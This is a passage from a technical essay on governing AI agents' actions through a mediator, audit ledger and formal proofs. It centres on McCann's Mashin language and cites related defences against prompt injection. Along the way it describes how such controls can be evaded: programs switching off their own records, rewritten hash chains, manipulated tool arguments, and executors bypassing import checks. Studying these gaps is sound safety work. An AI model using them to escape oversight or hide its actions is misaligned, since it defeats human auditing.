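`Ret(v)` is a program that has finished with the value `v`, and `Tau(t)` takes a silent step and continues as `t`. `Vis(e, k)` makes the request `e` and passes the reply to the function `k`. The refund program for $120 becomes a `Vis` node containing the payment request, and `k` turns the reply into the final text. Free monads usually represent finite programs, whereas interaction trees can also represent programs that may run forever, such as servers or long-running agents.

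Like Haskell's `IO` type, this structure keeps replies from being matched with the wrong requests. It also brings back the closed list of actions that Haskell gave up, since Mashin's formal model has exactly 14 kinds of request, including `HTTPRequest` and `LLMCall`. The mediator can inspect the current request, but it cannot see which requests will follow because k is a function.

McCann changes who controls the handler. A Skuld user chooses the handler and could write one that permits everything and records nothing. In Mashin, the runtime supplies the handler, and an operator G wraps checks and recording around it. McCann's *Effect-Transparent Governance for AI Workflow Architectures* (2026) defines the wrapped handler with a formula. In words, the wrapped handler runs the checks on request d and, if they pass, calls the original handler on d, records the outcome and returns the result.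 The program has no expression for attaching a handler, so it cannot remove the wrapper or put its own handler inside. McCann therefore describes his model as a specialization of algebraic effects. Programmers lose some freedom, since many use replaceable handlers to test code without touching real services. The `assuming` lines restore that freedom, but only for tests.

### Proposing everything first

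Other designs of early 2026 also separate a request from its execution. *Faramesh* (2026), a control layer for AI agents from January, treats an agent's proposal as untrusted and puts a deterministic authorization step between it and any real system. A design essay from February, *A Governed Model of Deterministic Program Execution* (2026), goes further than McCann in one respect, because its programs finish before anything happens:

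```haskell
Program : Input -> [Proposal]
Runtime : (State, Ledger, [Proposal]) -> (State, Ledger)
```

The program calculates a list of proposed changes to the world and stops. The runtime then admits, rejects or defers each proposal according to a "constitution", a function that can use the proposal, the current state and the whole ledger. A proposal may not contain branches, local variables or functions, so it remains a description that the runtime can read in full.

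This scheme would be awkward for a refund agent. The agent must look up an order before it can set the refund amount, but the program receives no replies. One proposal can declare that it depends on another, and the runtime will then perform them in order, but the later one cannot contain the earlier one's result. The agent would need two runs, one to fetch the order and another to take it as input and propose the refund. McCann's programs can do both in one run because `ask` returns a value.

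In exchange, the runtime has the complete plan before it acts. It could detect nine $100 refunds to the same customer and treat them as one $900 refund. McCann's mediator would receive them one at a time and could detect the pattern only if the context included earlier refunds. The essay's sample code also evaluates proposals one at a time, so it doesn't use the complete plan this way, but its constitution can check earlier entries in the ledger.

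Each proposal's identity is a cryptographic hash of its contents, so identical proposals have the same identity. The sample constitution rejects any proposal that has already succeeded. This rule prevents an accidental second payment for order A-1041, but it would also block a legitimate second payment if the proposal contained only a customer and an amount. Programmers would therefore have to include an order number or something else that distinguishes each intended action.

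### How much should one request cover?

A mediator can judge a request only by the information it contains. McCann points out that a compliance officer can understand a request to email a client with the subject "Invoice #4821", but not the Python web call that would send the same message. Mashin's standard library contains many readable requests like this. The example in *Lesson 4* posts a message to Microsoft Teams by giving a channel and a text, and the library handles authentication, retries and errors.

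A bare web request is harder to judge. Mashin's `http` permission covers both reading a weather forecast and charging a credit card. *HTTP / Storage Effects*, part of the specification for Kumiki, another language whose programs act only through effects, defines a separate capability for each HTTP method. A program could therefore have permission to fetch pages with GET but not to submit data with POST. This doesn't separate a refund from a charge when both are POST requests to the same company, because the difference is in their arguments. *TraceGrant* (2026), a security framework for AI agents that use online services, describes how attackers can change what a tool call does by controlling its arguments, without changing the tool. Its mediator therefore has to determine which object each call may affect and what evidence supports the arguments.

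Some requests cover too much. Mashin's `exec` action takes a string of Python, JavaScript or shell code, and the mediator receives one request however many things the script does. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) points out that policy layers that check each action separately miss network calls inside a Python script. The paper's system enforces its policy on the side effects it observes. In tests with coding agents, it blocked every attack within its scope, with a false-positive rate below 5 percent on harmless work.

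The most useful requests correspond to decisions that the policy's owner would recognize, such as refunding an order. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), for example, an agent that works on a bibliography gets three operations designed for that job and no general access to files. Somebody has to write those operations, and the code that turns each one into file or network access must be correct.

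In Mashin, a company could put the payment call in a separate refund machine that accepts only amounts up to $200, and let the agent call that machine without holding `http` itself. This would work if the called machine runs under its own rules, as Mashin's documentation describes. But McCann's paper limits a called program to permissions that its caller also has. Under that limit, the agent would need `http` to use the refund machine, and with `http` it could contact the payment company directly.

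Very small requests cause the opposite problem. A mediator can learn almost nothing from "Send these 1,500 bytes", because the bytes may be a fragment of an invoice or of a stolen customer list, and encryption would hide even that. Small requests are also slow. McCann measured a median overhead of 535 microseconds per request, nearly all of it spent writing to the ledger. At that rate, a program that requested each byte separately would need about nine minutes to send a megabyte. McCann says the overhead is less than 5 percent of a typical operation, which is right for a 100-millisecond web request. But it adds more than half to the time of a one-millisecond database query, which is at the fast end of his own range.

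Streaming fits the model badly. A voice call or a live data feed has no natural point at which to pause for approval. If the mediator approves the connection once, it has no information about what the program will send later. If it approves every fragment, it delays the stream, and each fragment provides little information. McCann acknowledges that his model cannot govern anything below the level of a single request, and leaves streaming to future work.

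## How is each request checked and recorded?

Mashin's mediator handles every request in a fixed order, with four checks before the effect and three steps after it, as McCann describes in *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance*. Here is the order for the $120 refund.

| Stage | What the mediator does | The $120 refund |
|---|---|---|
| Trust level | Looks up the rank of the program's code | The program ranks above untrusted code |
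| Permission | Compares the kind of action with the declared permissions | The program declares `http` |
| Phase | Checks which phase of execution the program is in | The program is running its steps |
| Hooks | Runs any extra checks attached at this point | A limit on amounts could go here |
| Effect | Performs the action | The payment company sends the money |
| Result check | Inspects the reply | The reply contains a refund number |
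| Record | Adds an entry to the ledger | The entry names the request and the decision |
| Broadcast | Announces the event to listeners | A dashboard might display the refund |

Each of the first four stages either passes or rejects the request, and the mediator stops at the first rejection. A request that needs approval waits at the permission stage until a person answers.

There are six trust levels: untrusted, tested, evaluated, reviewed, stdlib (the standard library) and system. According to *Algebraic Semantics of Governed Execution* (McCann, 2026), untrusted code can call only language models. The mediator would therefore refuse a refund request from an untrusted program even if it declared `http`.

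The result check runs after the external effect, so it cannot prevent it. In Mashin's documentation, a rule that performs this kind of check is called a *guard*, and it can block the data, redact it, log a warning or retry the step. Blocking the payment company's reply does not reverse the refund, and a retry could send a second one. Guards can also inspect a request before the effect, which is the only point at which they can stop it. In McCann's formal version of the mediator, the program receives the reply regardless of the result check's outcome.

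### Requests that always pass

Some requests go through the mediator but cannot be refused. McCann tested the runtime against its specification, which required it to accept every request from code at the stdlib and system levels, and never to deny three kinds of logging and broadcast request, whatever the program's trust level.

It makes sense to allow every log entry, because each refusal would leave a gap in the record. But the program chooses what a broadcast contains, so even an untrusted program can pass data to whoever is listening. The exemption for trusted code matters more, because marking a package as part of the standard library gives it access to the shell, the database and the network, and no permission rule will stop the package from misusing them. Deciding who may assign trust levels is as important as writing the policy.

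### Why the check always finishes

Suppose the refund company's policy has three rules:

1. Deny a refund above $500.
2. Hold a refund above $200 for approval.
3. Allow a POST request to the payment company's refund address.

The mediator denies anything that matches no rule, and when several rules match, it follows the strictest. A $350 refund matches the second and third rules, so the mediator holds it.

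This procedure always ends with an answer because there are finitely many rules, the request is a finite piece of data, and each rule is a simple test, such as comparing two numbers or looking up a name in a list. McCann requires every rule to be a function that returns true or false on all inputs. There is no such guarantee when predicting what an arbitrary program will do. McCann concedes that the mathematics is trivial and says the contribution is the design of a language where every action arrives as a finite piece of data.

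The guarantee that every rule returns a result excludes some rules that companies would want. A rule may not query a fraud-scoring service during the check, because the service might never reply. The runtime would have to fetch the score first and include it in the request's context. Hooks must also be guaranteed to finish, since an endless loop in one would stall the mediator. A rule that always returns a result can still return the wrong one, such as when a filter for personal data misses a name.

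### Rules about earlier actions

To catch a large refund split into several small ones, a mediator has to remember earlier requests. Other rules depend on the replies as well. Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Sapien*, describe a policy engine for AI agents that keeps both. A Sapien policy specifies permitted sequences of tool calls with a regular expression, a notation that programmers normally use for patterns in text, extended with variables. For the task "Pay my Acme invoice", a policy could be:

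```
list_invoices@inv . pay(vendor="Acme", amount=PREDICATE(is_due))
```

The dot means "followed by", and `@inv` stores the first call and its reply in the variable `inv`. The short Python function `is_due` looks for the proposed amount among Acme's invoices in `inv`.

Sapien turns the policy into an automaton, a set of states connected by permitted calls. This one needs three main states: nothing done, invoices read and invoice paid. Only `list_invoices` leads out of the first state, so Sapien refuses any payment before the agent reads the invoices. If the reply shows that Acme is owed $130, Sapien accepts a payment of $130 to Acme but refuses a payment of $900 to Acme or of any amount to another company. No call leads out of the third state, so the agent cannot pay the invoice twice.

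Sometimes the history fits a policy in more than one way. An agent that has to forward an invoice and answer a question from Bob may search the inbox twice before doing either. The history does not yet determine which search belongs to which job, so Sapien keeps both interpretations, each with its own values for the variables. When the agent forwards a message, Sapien discards any interpretation in which that message did not come from the invoice search.

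Tiffany and colleagues tested the policies assuming that an attacker fully controlled the agent. On AgentDojo, a set of short office, travel and banking tasks, Sapien blocked 93 to 95 percent of 949 attacks, compared with 83 to 87 percent for a plain list of permitted tools. On Toolathlon, which has longer tasks, the attacks misused tools that the agent needed for its work. Sapien blocked 65 percent of these 212 attacks, compared with 32 percent for the list. Most of the successful attacks depended on the meaning of content, such as a false statement in a file the agent was supposed to write.

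Rules with memory can still be wrong. A language model writes each Sapien policy from the user's request and sometimes makes it too loose or too strict. Writing the policy took an average of 148 seconds per task on Toolathlon. Sapien's rules can also contain arbitrary Python, so they lack McCann's guarantee that every check finishes.

Mashin's mediator could apply rules like these if the context of each request included the relevant history. The decision record in McCann's calculus would not be enough, because it contains the request, decision, policy applied, context and previous entry's hash, but not the reply. The working ledger also stores each step's output by default, according to Mashin's *records*.

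### A program can switch off its own record

According to *Records*, a Mashin program can include a section that disables whole categories of ledger entry, including the mediator's decisions. When those entries are disabled, the mediator still checks the program's requests but doesn't record its decisions. McCann's calculus has no such setting, and one of its theorems is that every request adds exactly one record.

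Mashin strongly discourages using the setting in production. But an AI agent that writes its own programs could still use it, and the resulting actions would not be governed effects because the decision would go unrecorded. The runtime could prevent this by taking the setting from the operator instead of the program. By default, the runtime also deletes entries after 90 days, so an auditor who looks later may find nothing unless someone has extended the period.

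### How the hash chain works

Mashin links its ledger entries with hashes to make later changes detectable. A hash function turns data of any length into a short value, and a cryptographic one, such as the SHA-256 function that Mashin uses, is designed so that nobody can feasibly find two inputs with the same value. McCann defines the hash of entry k as

hₖ = H(rₖ ‖ hₖ₋₁)

where rₖ is the record, ‖ joins two pieces of data, and h₀ is a fixed starting value. Each hash therefore depends on every earlier entry.

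A toy hash function could multiply the previous hash by 31, add the refund amount in dollars, and keep the last three digits. If h₀ is 7, the first entry, for $120, gets the hash 31 × 7 + 120 = 337. The second entry, for $350, gives 31 × 337 + 350 = 10,797, so its hash is 797.

| Entry | Decision | Original amount | Original hash | Rewritten amount | Rewritten hash |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Allowed | $120 | 337 | $20 | 237 |
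| 2 | Held | $350 | 797 | $350 | 697 |
| 3 | Denied | $900 | 607 | $900 | 507 |

Suppose an employee wants to hide $100 by changing the first amount to $20. If the employee leaves the old hash in place, an auditor who recalculates it gets 237 instead of 337 and detects the change. If the employee also replaces that hash, the second entry no longer matches. But an employee who controls the whole ledger can recalculate all three hashes, and the rewritten chain passes every test the original passed.

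As the example shows, the ledger and the hash function are not enough to verify the record when the ledger's holder is under suspicion, because anyone can run SHA-256, so the holder could change an event and recompute the hashes. McCann writes that an auditor needs only those two things and does not have to trust the governance system, but *Algebraic Semantics of Governed Execution* proves only that changing an event makes its entry invalid if the stored hash stays the same. *Event ledger*, part of the documentation for a smaller agent runtime called Odinn, openly acknowledges that its hash chain is not tamper-proof against an attacker who controls the runtime's data directory.

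Deleting the newest entries is even easier, because the employee doesn't have to recalculate anything. Without the third entry, the first two still form a valid chain. McCann proves that any initial part of a valid chain is also valid.

The remedy is to keep a copy of the latest hash where the ledger's holder cannot change it. If the auditor wrote down 607 on Monday evening, they can detect a rewritten chain whose third hash is 507 or a chain with only two entries. The holder can still rewrite newer entries undetected until the auditor takes another copy.

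*AMP* (2020), a system for certifying the origin of photographs and videos, gives evidence to more parties. Its ledger service occasionally signs a single hash that covers all the entries, and publishers get signed receipts for their own entries. A publisher can later use its receipt to prove that an entry existed, without contacting the service. In the refund example, the payment company could hold such receipts.

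Hardware can also protect the log from some of the people who might alter it. *Trusted AI Agents in the Cloud* (Bodea, Misono and colleagues, 2025) presents Omega, which runs agents, policy checks and a tamper-evident log inside a virtual machine whose memory the processor shields from the cloud company. Omega protects against a dishonest cloud operator but not against physical attacks on the machine, and it relies on the processor and its own trusted software.

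### What a crash can lose

McCann's papers differ on when the mediator writes the record. In *Intent-Driven Computing*, it records the decision and then performs the action. In *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance*, it performs the action first, so a computer crash between the two steps would leave the action unrecorded.

If the mediator acts before recording a request, a crash can leave a payment with no entry in the ledger. An auditor would find $120 missing and no record of a request for it. Refused requests also get no entry at the record stage, because the mediator stops before reaching it.

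If the mediator records each action before performing it, every action has an entry, but the ledger may also contain entries for actions that never happened. After a crash, the ledger shows that the mediator allowed a refund, but not whether the payment company received the request. Diagrid's *Verifiable Execution* acknowledges this limitation in the company's own product, which writes a signed record before each step, and advises users to check the external system. Recording first is better for an audit because a person can investigate an uncertain entry but has no reason to look for a missing one.

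Odinn records the request and then the decision before the action runs, and records the result afterwards. If an allowed request has no recorded result, someone needs to check what happened. The runtime should not simply repeat the request, because the first attempt may have succeeded. Repeating it is safe only if the payment company can recognise a duplicate, for instance because both attempts carry the same identifier.

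None of these problems can arise in the calculus of *Intent-Driven Computing*, because a single rule performs the action and extends the ledger in one indivisible step. Real computers have no such step. In McCann's test configuration, an entry could disappear even if the mediator recorded it before acting. The ledger was an SQLite database that did not force each record onto the disk, so the newest entries could remain in the operating system's memory for a while. They would survive a crash of the Mashin runtime but not necessarily a power failure. The mediator could record a refund, send it and lose the record when the power went out. The remaining entries would still form a valid chain, so the hashes would not reveal the loss.

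Distributed databases solve this problem by forcing records to disk before sending any message that depends on them. *Events and actions*, from the documentation for a small library that keeps copies of a log consistent across machines, states this rule. Mashin could follow it, but then every request would have to wait for the disk.

### What checking and recording cost

McCann measured the mediator on an Apple M4 Pro computer over 10,000 runs. Evaluating 20 rules took a median of one microsecond, and computing a hash took less than one, so the ledger write accounts for nearly all of the 535-microsecond total. The write took 560 microseconds when measured by itself, so the two figures probably come from separate runs. The slowest 1 percent of runs took at least 1,186 microseconds in total.

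McCann's figure of less than 5 percent overhead does not hold for web requests that take 10 milliseconds or database queries that take 1 millisecond, the low ends of his two ranges.

| Operation | Time without the mediator | Added at the median | Added in the slowest 1 percent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast database query | 1 ms | 53.5% | At least 119% |
| Fast web request | 10 ms | 5.4% | At least 11.9% |
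| Ordinary web request | 100 ms | 0.5% | At least 1.2% |

At the median, the claim holds only for operations longer than 10.7 milliseconds. This includes calls to language models and most web services, which take up much of an agent's time, but not a program that makes thousands of short database queries. Forcing every record onto the disk would raise the overhead further.

The chain also limits how fast the mediator can record requests, because each entry needs the hash of the one before it. At McCann's average of 591 microseconds per request, a single chain could record about 1,700 requests a second. Giving each program its own chain would raise the limit, but an auditor would then need a copy of the latest hash from every chain.

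*Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance* reports a much lower overhead. Over 50 runs, McCann measured a median of 0.23 milliseconds with governance and 0.24 without, and calls the overhead effectively zero. An extra step cannot make a program faster, so the difference is noise. The governed run took less than half as long as the ledger write in the other test, so it almost certainly did not include the same kind of write. That makes 535 microseconds the better estimate for a mediator that keeps a lasting record.

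### Replaying old requests under a new policy

A complete ledger lets a company test a policy before adopting it. The mediator applies the new rules to each recorded request and its context, then reports the new decision, without running the program or performing any action.

McCann tried this on the 847 requests from the simulated refund agent. When he raised the refund limit from $500 to $1,000, 89 of the 312 denials became approvals. The other 223 stayed denied, since a higher limit does not affect requests for the wrong customer's records. The new policy must not have held the 89 larger refunds for a person to review, although the original policy held some smaller ones. If the company wanted a person to review them, they would add to the 112 held requests.

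The replay shows how the new policy would have judged the old requests, but not which requests the agent would have made under it. Suppose the agent asked to refund a customer $800, was refused, and then asked to refund the same customer $500. Under the new limit, the replay approves both, for a total of $1,300. Had that limit been in force at the time, the first refund would have gone through and the agent would have had no reason to ask for a second. It might instead have asked to email the customer a confirmation, but the ledger has no such request because the agent never made it. The replay is therefore reliable only up to the first decision that changes, and later results are guesses.

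The decision in one case can also change the context for later cases. McCann notes that a replay needs either the recorded context or a way to reconstruct it. Using the recorded context makes the replay repeatable, but that context doesn't reflect the replay's new decisions. If the policy capped refunds at $10,000 a day, the recorded daily totals would leave out the 89 newly approved payments, and the replay could approve requests that the cap should have stopped.

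Privacy settings can prevent a replay altogether. Mashin can mask, hash or drop chosen fields when it writes an entry, and nobody can recover the original values from the ledger. If a company masks the refund amounts, it cannot test a new limit on them. Hashed amounts would show whether two refunds were equal, but not whether either exceeded $1,000.

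## What has been proved about such a language?

A mediator's checks are useless if a program can act without going through them. McCann has written machine-checked proofs that this cannot happen in a mathematical model of Mashin. He used Rocq (formerly Coq), a proof assistant in which people write definitions, theorems and proofs, and a small program called the kernel checks every step. Anyone who trusts the kernel can skip the proofs, but they still have to read the definitions and theorems. *SoK* (2026), a survey of verification tools for a type of cryptographic software, warns that a vacuous or misstated theorem passes the kernel "while establishing nothing".

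McCann's papers usually report 454 theorems in 36 files, with none "admitted", which in Rocq means accepted without proof. The project's GitHub account, mashin-live, lists 548 theorems in 32 files. McCann's breakdown of the theorems by type also adds up to 548, so that total is probably current. By his count, 30 are core results that contain the mathematical content, and another 56 mostly confirm that a definition covers every case.

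### A program as a tree

The interaction trees in McCann's proofs branch wherever a program makes a request and waits for a reply. Xia, Zakowski and colleagues (2019), in *Interaction Trees*, introduced the structure with examples such as a program that reads numbers until it receives a 9:

```
read a number
 ├─ 9             →  stop
 └─ anything else →  read a number
                      ├─ 9             →  stop
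                      └─ anything else →  ...
```

The tree covers every possible reply, including an endless series of numbers that never includes a 9. Xia and colleagues also define `spin`, a program that takes silent steps forever without making a request or returning a result. McCann uses `spin` to represent a refusal.

His operator G replaces each request in a program's tree with a larger piece of tree. The $120 refund becomes:

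```
trust level?
 ├─ no  → spin
 └─ yes → permission?
           ├─ no  → spin
           └─ yes → phase?
                     ├─ no  → spin
                     └─ yes → hooks?
                               ├─ no  → spin
                               └─ yes → SEND THE PAYMENT

→ check the result

→ record

→ broadcast

→ the rest of the program
```

The payment is an *I/O event* (input or output), and the other seven stages are *governance events*. The handler, a function h, carries out the payment. McCann writes interp(G(h), t) for the program t after G has wrapped each of its requests.

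### The main theorem

McCann's safety property, `gov_safe`, applies to a tree and a flag that is either true or false. The flag records whether I/O is currently permitted. With the rules that McCann describes in *Effect-Transparent Governance for AI Workflow Architectures*, a tree is safe in these cases:

```
finished:          always
silent step:       if the rest is safe with the same flag
governance event:  if, for every answer, the rest is safe with the flag true
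I/O event:         if the flag is already true and, for every reply,
                   the rest is safe with the flag true
```

The main theorem is that, for every handler h and every program t,

gov_safe(false, interp(G(h), t))

In words, a wrapped program is safe even when the flag starts as false.

A short lemma shows that `gov_safe` excludes any tree that begins with an I/O event while the flag is false, since no rule makes such a tree safe. This matters because if `gov_safe` accepted every tree, the main theorem would be true but useless.

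The main theorem needs a proof that works for programs that run forever, so McCann cannot use induction on a program's length. He uses coinduction instead, showing that the next part of the tree obeys the rules and then assuming the theorem for whatever follows. There are three cases:

- The program has finished. Nothing is left to check.
- The program takes a silent step. The wrapped program takes the same step, and the theorem applies to the rest.
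- The program makes a request. G puts a governance event first, which turns the flag true. If any of the four checks fails, the tree continues as `spin`, which is safe because it contains no I/O. If all four pass, the handler runs. It may perform any number of I/O events, even infinitely many, so McCann uses a second coinduction here, but every event occurs with the flag true. After the three closing events, the theorem applies to the rest of the program.

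At 213 lines, this is the longest proof in the collection.

### A weak property and a stronger construction

Under these rules, any governance event sets the flag to true, whether the request is allowed or refused, and the flag never becomes false again. `gov_safe` therefore means only that no I/O happens before the first governance event. A faulty mediator could satisfy `gov_safe` and still pay a $900 refund after the check refuses it, or check a program's first request and none of the later ones.

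*Zero-Trust Formal Methods* (2026) describes the same kind of gap in software that AI agents wrote and verified. The agents built programs that check claims that a logical formula has no solution, and proved that these programs never accept a false claim. But a checker that secretly copied its input to an extra output channel would also satisfy the theorem, and only a person reviewing the specification could catch this.

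G's short definition shows that it makes neither of the mistakes in the refund examples. The handler appears in only one branch, which the program reaches after all four checks have passed, and `interp` applies G separately to every request. Each request in the model therefore gets its own checks before its handler runs. This is the guarantee a company would want. It holds because of how McCann built G, and the main theorem does not state it.

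*Algebraic Semantics of Governed Execution* contains two properties that come closer to stating the guarantee. In that paper, McCann describes a stricter `gov_safe`, in which a failed check turns the flag false and so does every I/O event. He also defines a *well-governed trace*. A trace is the list of events in one run, and it is well-governed if at least one passing check precedes every I/O event. The definitions disagree about some simple runs:

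| Run | `gov_safe`, original rules | `gov_safe`, stricter rules | Well-governed trace |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pay $120 without a check | Rejected | Rejected | Rejected |
| Check fails, pay $900 | Accepted | Rejected | Rejected |
| Check passes, pay $120, pay $900 | Accepted | Rejected | Accepted |
| Check passes, pay $120, check passes, pay $900 | Accepted | Accepted | Accepted |

The stricter `gov_safe` comes closest to requiring a check for every request, but it would make the main theorem false. The theorem covers every handler, including one that responds to a refund request by sending the payment and then emailing a receipt. Under the stricter rules, the payment sets the flag to false, which makes the email unsafe. McCann's code in *Effect-Transparent Governance for AI Workflow Architectures* leaves the flag true after I/O, and his account of the proof also allows several I/O events per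 request, so the stricter rules appear to be a mistake in the description.

The trace property improves on the original `gov_safe` because a failed check no longer counts. However, one passing check is still enough for every later action, as the third row shows. Under the original rules, `gov_safe` alone does not guarantee well-governed traces, as the second row shows, although McCann's name for the theorem connecting the two properties suggests that it does. Programs wrapped in G do produce well-governed traces, again because of how G works.

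None of these properties could link a check to a particular payment. In McCann's model, a governance event contains the name of a stage, such as "permission", but not the request. The four checks in the definition of G do not take the request as an input either. If a mediator approved a $120 refund and then paid $900, its governance events would be the same as those of a mediator that paid the approved amount. McCann could state the per-request guarantee as a theorem by giving each request an identifier and including it in both governance and I/O events. The proof should not be much harder, since G already behaves as the theorem would require.

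The main theorem also leaves the handler's conduct open. It covers every handler, including one that sends the customer's refund to somebody else.

Andrici, Ciobâcă and colleagues (2023), in *Securing Verified IO Programs Against Unverified Code in F\**, prove a more informative property. They link a verified program with untrusted code, which must do all its I/O through a library that checks an access policy before each operation. Their events include the operation's arguments and result, so a theorem can describe what the code did. In their main example, a verified web server uses an untrusted component to answer requests. They enforce, among other properties, that this component opens and reads files only from a particular folder. The policy can also depend on earlier events, such as whether a file is already open.

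The result from Andrici and colleagues is also limited to untrusted code written in a restricted part of F*, a language for writing programs together with proofs, and to a model in which I/O is the only side effect. They consider a secure compiler for realistic programs a long-term goal. Still, their work shows that a proof about mediated I/O can cover both the content of each action and whether a check came first.

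### The two boundaries as a theorem

McCann's claim that a language's expressiveness boundary and governance boundary coincide is also stated as a theorem, E = G, in *Algebraic Semantics of Governed Execution*. The set E contains the expressible programs, which are built from four primitives: CODE for pure computation, REASON for calls to a language model, MEMORY for storage and CALL for invoking another machine. The set G (not the operator of the same name) contains the programs that satisfy `gov_safe` once the operator has wrapped them.

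The Rocq theorem proves half of this, that every program in E is in G. This already follows from the main theorem, which applies to all programs in the model. McCann writes that the other half, that every program in G is in E, "follows from the construction". Whether it does depends on how one reads the definition of E. If E contains every tree of requests, both sets contain everything in the model and their equality adds no information. If E contains only the programs built from the four primitives, the sets seem to differ. A program that sends a web request directly is in G by the main theorem, but it doesn't seem to be in E, because CALL, the closest primitive, only invokes other machines.

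This mismatch does not weaken safety, because the extra programs are governed too. The larger limitation is that the model cannot represent an ungoverned effect in a program. A program in the model can only calculate, make one of the 14 kinds of request or finish. The theorem confirms that the definitions are consistent with each other, but it cannot establish that a real Mashin program has no other way to act, because the model assumes this.

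A second condition of coterminous governance is that the primitives be sufficient for the intended computations. McCann addresses it by translating register machines into his model. A register machine is a simple computer that can only add to, subtract from and test a few stored numbers, but it can compute anything computable if time and the size of the numbers are unlimited. In the theorem called "governed Turing completeness", McCann proves only that the translated programs satisfy `gov_safe`, so it is another case of the main theorem. Separate theorems show that the translation computes the right results, assuming that the memory handler correctly stores and returns values. Each translated program runs for at most a fixed number of steps, but whoever translates it can set this limit as high as they like.

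In this translation, even adding one to a number requires a memory request that passes through the mediator, whereas pure code in the calculus of *Intent-Driven Computing* can do any calculation without a request. Because the two models differ in which operations count as effects, a proof about one doesn't automatically apply to the other.

### Why some results are nearly immediate

In the calculus, no action can bypass the mediator, a property McCann calls "non-bypass". The proof takes a few lines because only the Allow rule performs actions, and it requires the mediator's approval. McCann cites `GovernanceMediation.v` for the machine-checked version, but the module index in *Algebraic Semantics of Governed Execution* does not list that file, although he describes the index as complete.

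An easy proof is a good sign in a language design because it makes clear why the property holds. However, a single rule that let a program bypass the checking or recording of effects would make the theorem false.

Mashin programs can generate other programs, which can generate more, and McCann proves that governance holds at every level in the model. He defines a program the same way at each level, as a tree of requests, so the theorem for each level is the main theorem with a different label. The definition assumes that the runtime sends a newly generated program's requests through the same mediator, but whether this holds is the difficult question for a real system.

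McCann presents another result as a comparison with content filters, which inspect or change a system's output. He proves that any handler, including one that filters content, is safe when G wraps it, and that unwrapped I/O is unsafe whatever filter it has. These two claims repeat the main theorem and the lemma about bare I/O. `gov_safe` only requires governance events to come before I/O, so a mediator could pass while approving every harmful message, and an unwrapped filter would fail even if it blocked them all. The comparison therefore cannot show which approach prevents more harm.

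Another theorem about G is that if every check passes, a wrapped program performs the same I/O in the same order as the original and returns the same result. The theorem rules out a mediator that makes every program loop forever, even though such a mediator would satisfy `gov_safe`.

In the proofs, a run loops forever if the mediator refuses a request, and the theorem does not cover such runs. McCann chose looping because it fits easily into proofs by coinduction, but he concedes that it may obscure refusals in practice. The main theorem would probably still hold if a refusal returned a value, as it does in the calculus, because G would also wrap the program's next request.

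The theorems about the ledger are also limited. McCann proves that the ledger contains every event in a trace and no others. But in the model, a function builds the ledger from the trace, so the theorem shows that this function copies events correctly. It does not show that a running mediator writes each entry, or that the entry survives a crash. The proofs also assume a hash function that never gives two inputs the same value. No function that shortens data can meet this assumption, and McCann leaves the connection to real hash functions as future work.

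### Testing the runtime against the model

*Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (2026) notes that a proof checker can confirm that a theorem follows from its definitions, but applying the theorem to a deployed system requires further assumptions, which the designers should state. McCann's proofs assume that the runtime implements the model faithfully, and he supports this assumption mainly with tests.

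McCann wrote a 148-line reference interpreter that restates part of the Rocq specification in Elixir, the language of the Mashin runtime. A test program generates random sequences of requests with random trust levels and permissions, then compares the interpreter's decisions with the runtime's. It tests seven properties on 10,000 inputs each. One property is that the two always make the same decision, and another is that raising a program's trust level never takes away a permission. Another 36 tests each correspond to a particular theorem. He reports no remaining mismatches.

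The tests found a bug on the 188th random input, which contained a request to run an operating system command. The program had the necessary permission, so the specification allowed the request, but the runtime denied it. One part of the runtime called the permission `compute.exec`, while the list of permissions had it only as `compute.code.execute`. Ordinary tests of the separate parts had missed the mismatch because each part worked correctly by itself. McCann fixed the bug by adding the missing name to the list.

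This is good evidence that comparing a runtime with a formal specification finds real mistakes. The mistake was on the safe side, because the runtime blocked a command it should have allowed. The tests could also have found the opposite error, where the runtime allows a forbidden request, but McCann does not report one.

Random tests cannot prove that no mistakes remain. If a property holds on 10,000 random inputs, one can be 95 percent confident that it fails on fewer than about 3 in 10,000 inputs drawn in the same way. Rare failures are still possible, and an agent looking for a way around a refusal does not choose its requests at random. When there are few cases, it is better to test all of them, as McCann does for the combinations of trust level and permission.

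He also reduces the gap by running some of the proved code. Rocq can translate definitions into OCaml, an ordinary programming language, and the Mashin runtime can call the result. The translated functions compare trust levels, look up permissions and determine whether to allow a request. McCann has not verified the C code that connects them to the runtime. If the translated code is unavailable, the runtime uses an Elixir version, which the proofs do not cover.

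McCann does not list the operator G or the function `interp` among the translated functions. The proved code can therefore decide whether a refund is allowed, but ordinary Elixir code has to call it for every refund and enforce the result. The main theorem is about this step. McCann also proves that whenever the decision function allows a request, the wrapped request satisfies `gov_safe`. This theorem is meant to connect the decision function to `gov_safe`, but every wrapped request satisfies `gov_safe`, including those the function denies, so the theorem gives no evidence that the decisions are right.

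*Agenra* (2026) uses a similar division of work to control AI agents. Its Python code forwards each tool call to functions verified in Lean, another proof assistant, which allow or block the call. The paper lists the Python code and the behaviour of the external tools among the parts that users have to trust. If the Python code failed to forward a call, the verified functions could not block it.

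McCann has tested whether Mashin's runtime matches the model, but has not proved that it does. He says that his tests connect the two by "the same methodology as seL4", an operating system kernel, but this overstates the similarity. Klein, Andronick and colleagues (2009) proved that seL4's C code always follows its specification, assuming that the compiler, the assembly code and the hardware were correct. The seL4 project later extended the proof to the compiled program, so users no longer have to trust the compiler or linker. As the project explains, testing can find bugs but, unlike a proof, cannot show that there are none.

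Even seL4's proofs depend on some assumptions, and its proof of confidentiality does not cover information that leaks through the timing of operations. Mashin's proofs make a broader assumption, that programs can act only through requests. The random tests cannot check this assumption because they compare the specification's decisions with the runtime's, and an action taken without a request produces no decisions to compare.

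## What stops the host from offering a way round?

McCann's proofs assume that programs can act only through requests, but whether this is true depends on the host. Mashin runs on the Erlang virtual machine, where code can normally open connections, write files and start other programs. In *Certified Purity for Cognitive Workflow Executors*, McCann examines *executors*, the modules that carry out a program's steps. An executor receives a step's settings and returns a result with a list of effect requests for the mediator.

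Mashin originally used an import check to stop executors from acting directly. The check rejected any executor that depended on a module for input or output. McCann then found five ways an author who knows the design could pass the check and still act without permission.

### Five gaps in the Erlang virtual machine

| Gap | What code can do | Why an import check misses it |
|---|---|---|
| Dynamic calls | Call a function whose name it works out while running | The name is not among the imports |
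| Runtime evaluation | Build program text and have the virtual machine run it | The text may not exist until the program runs |
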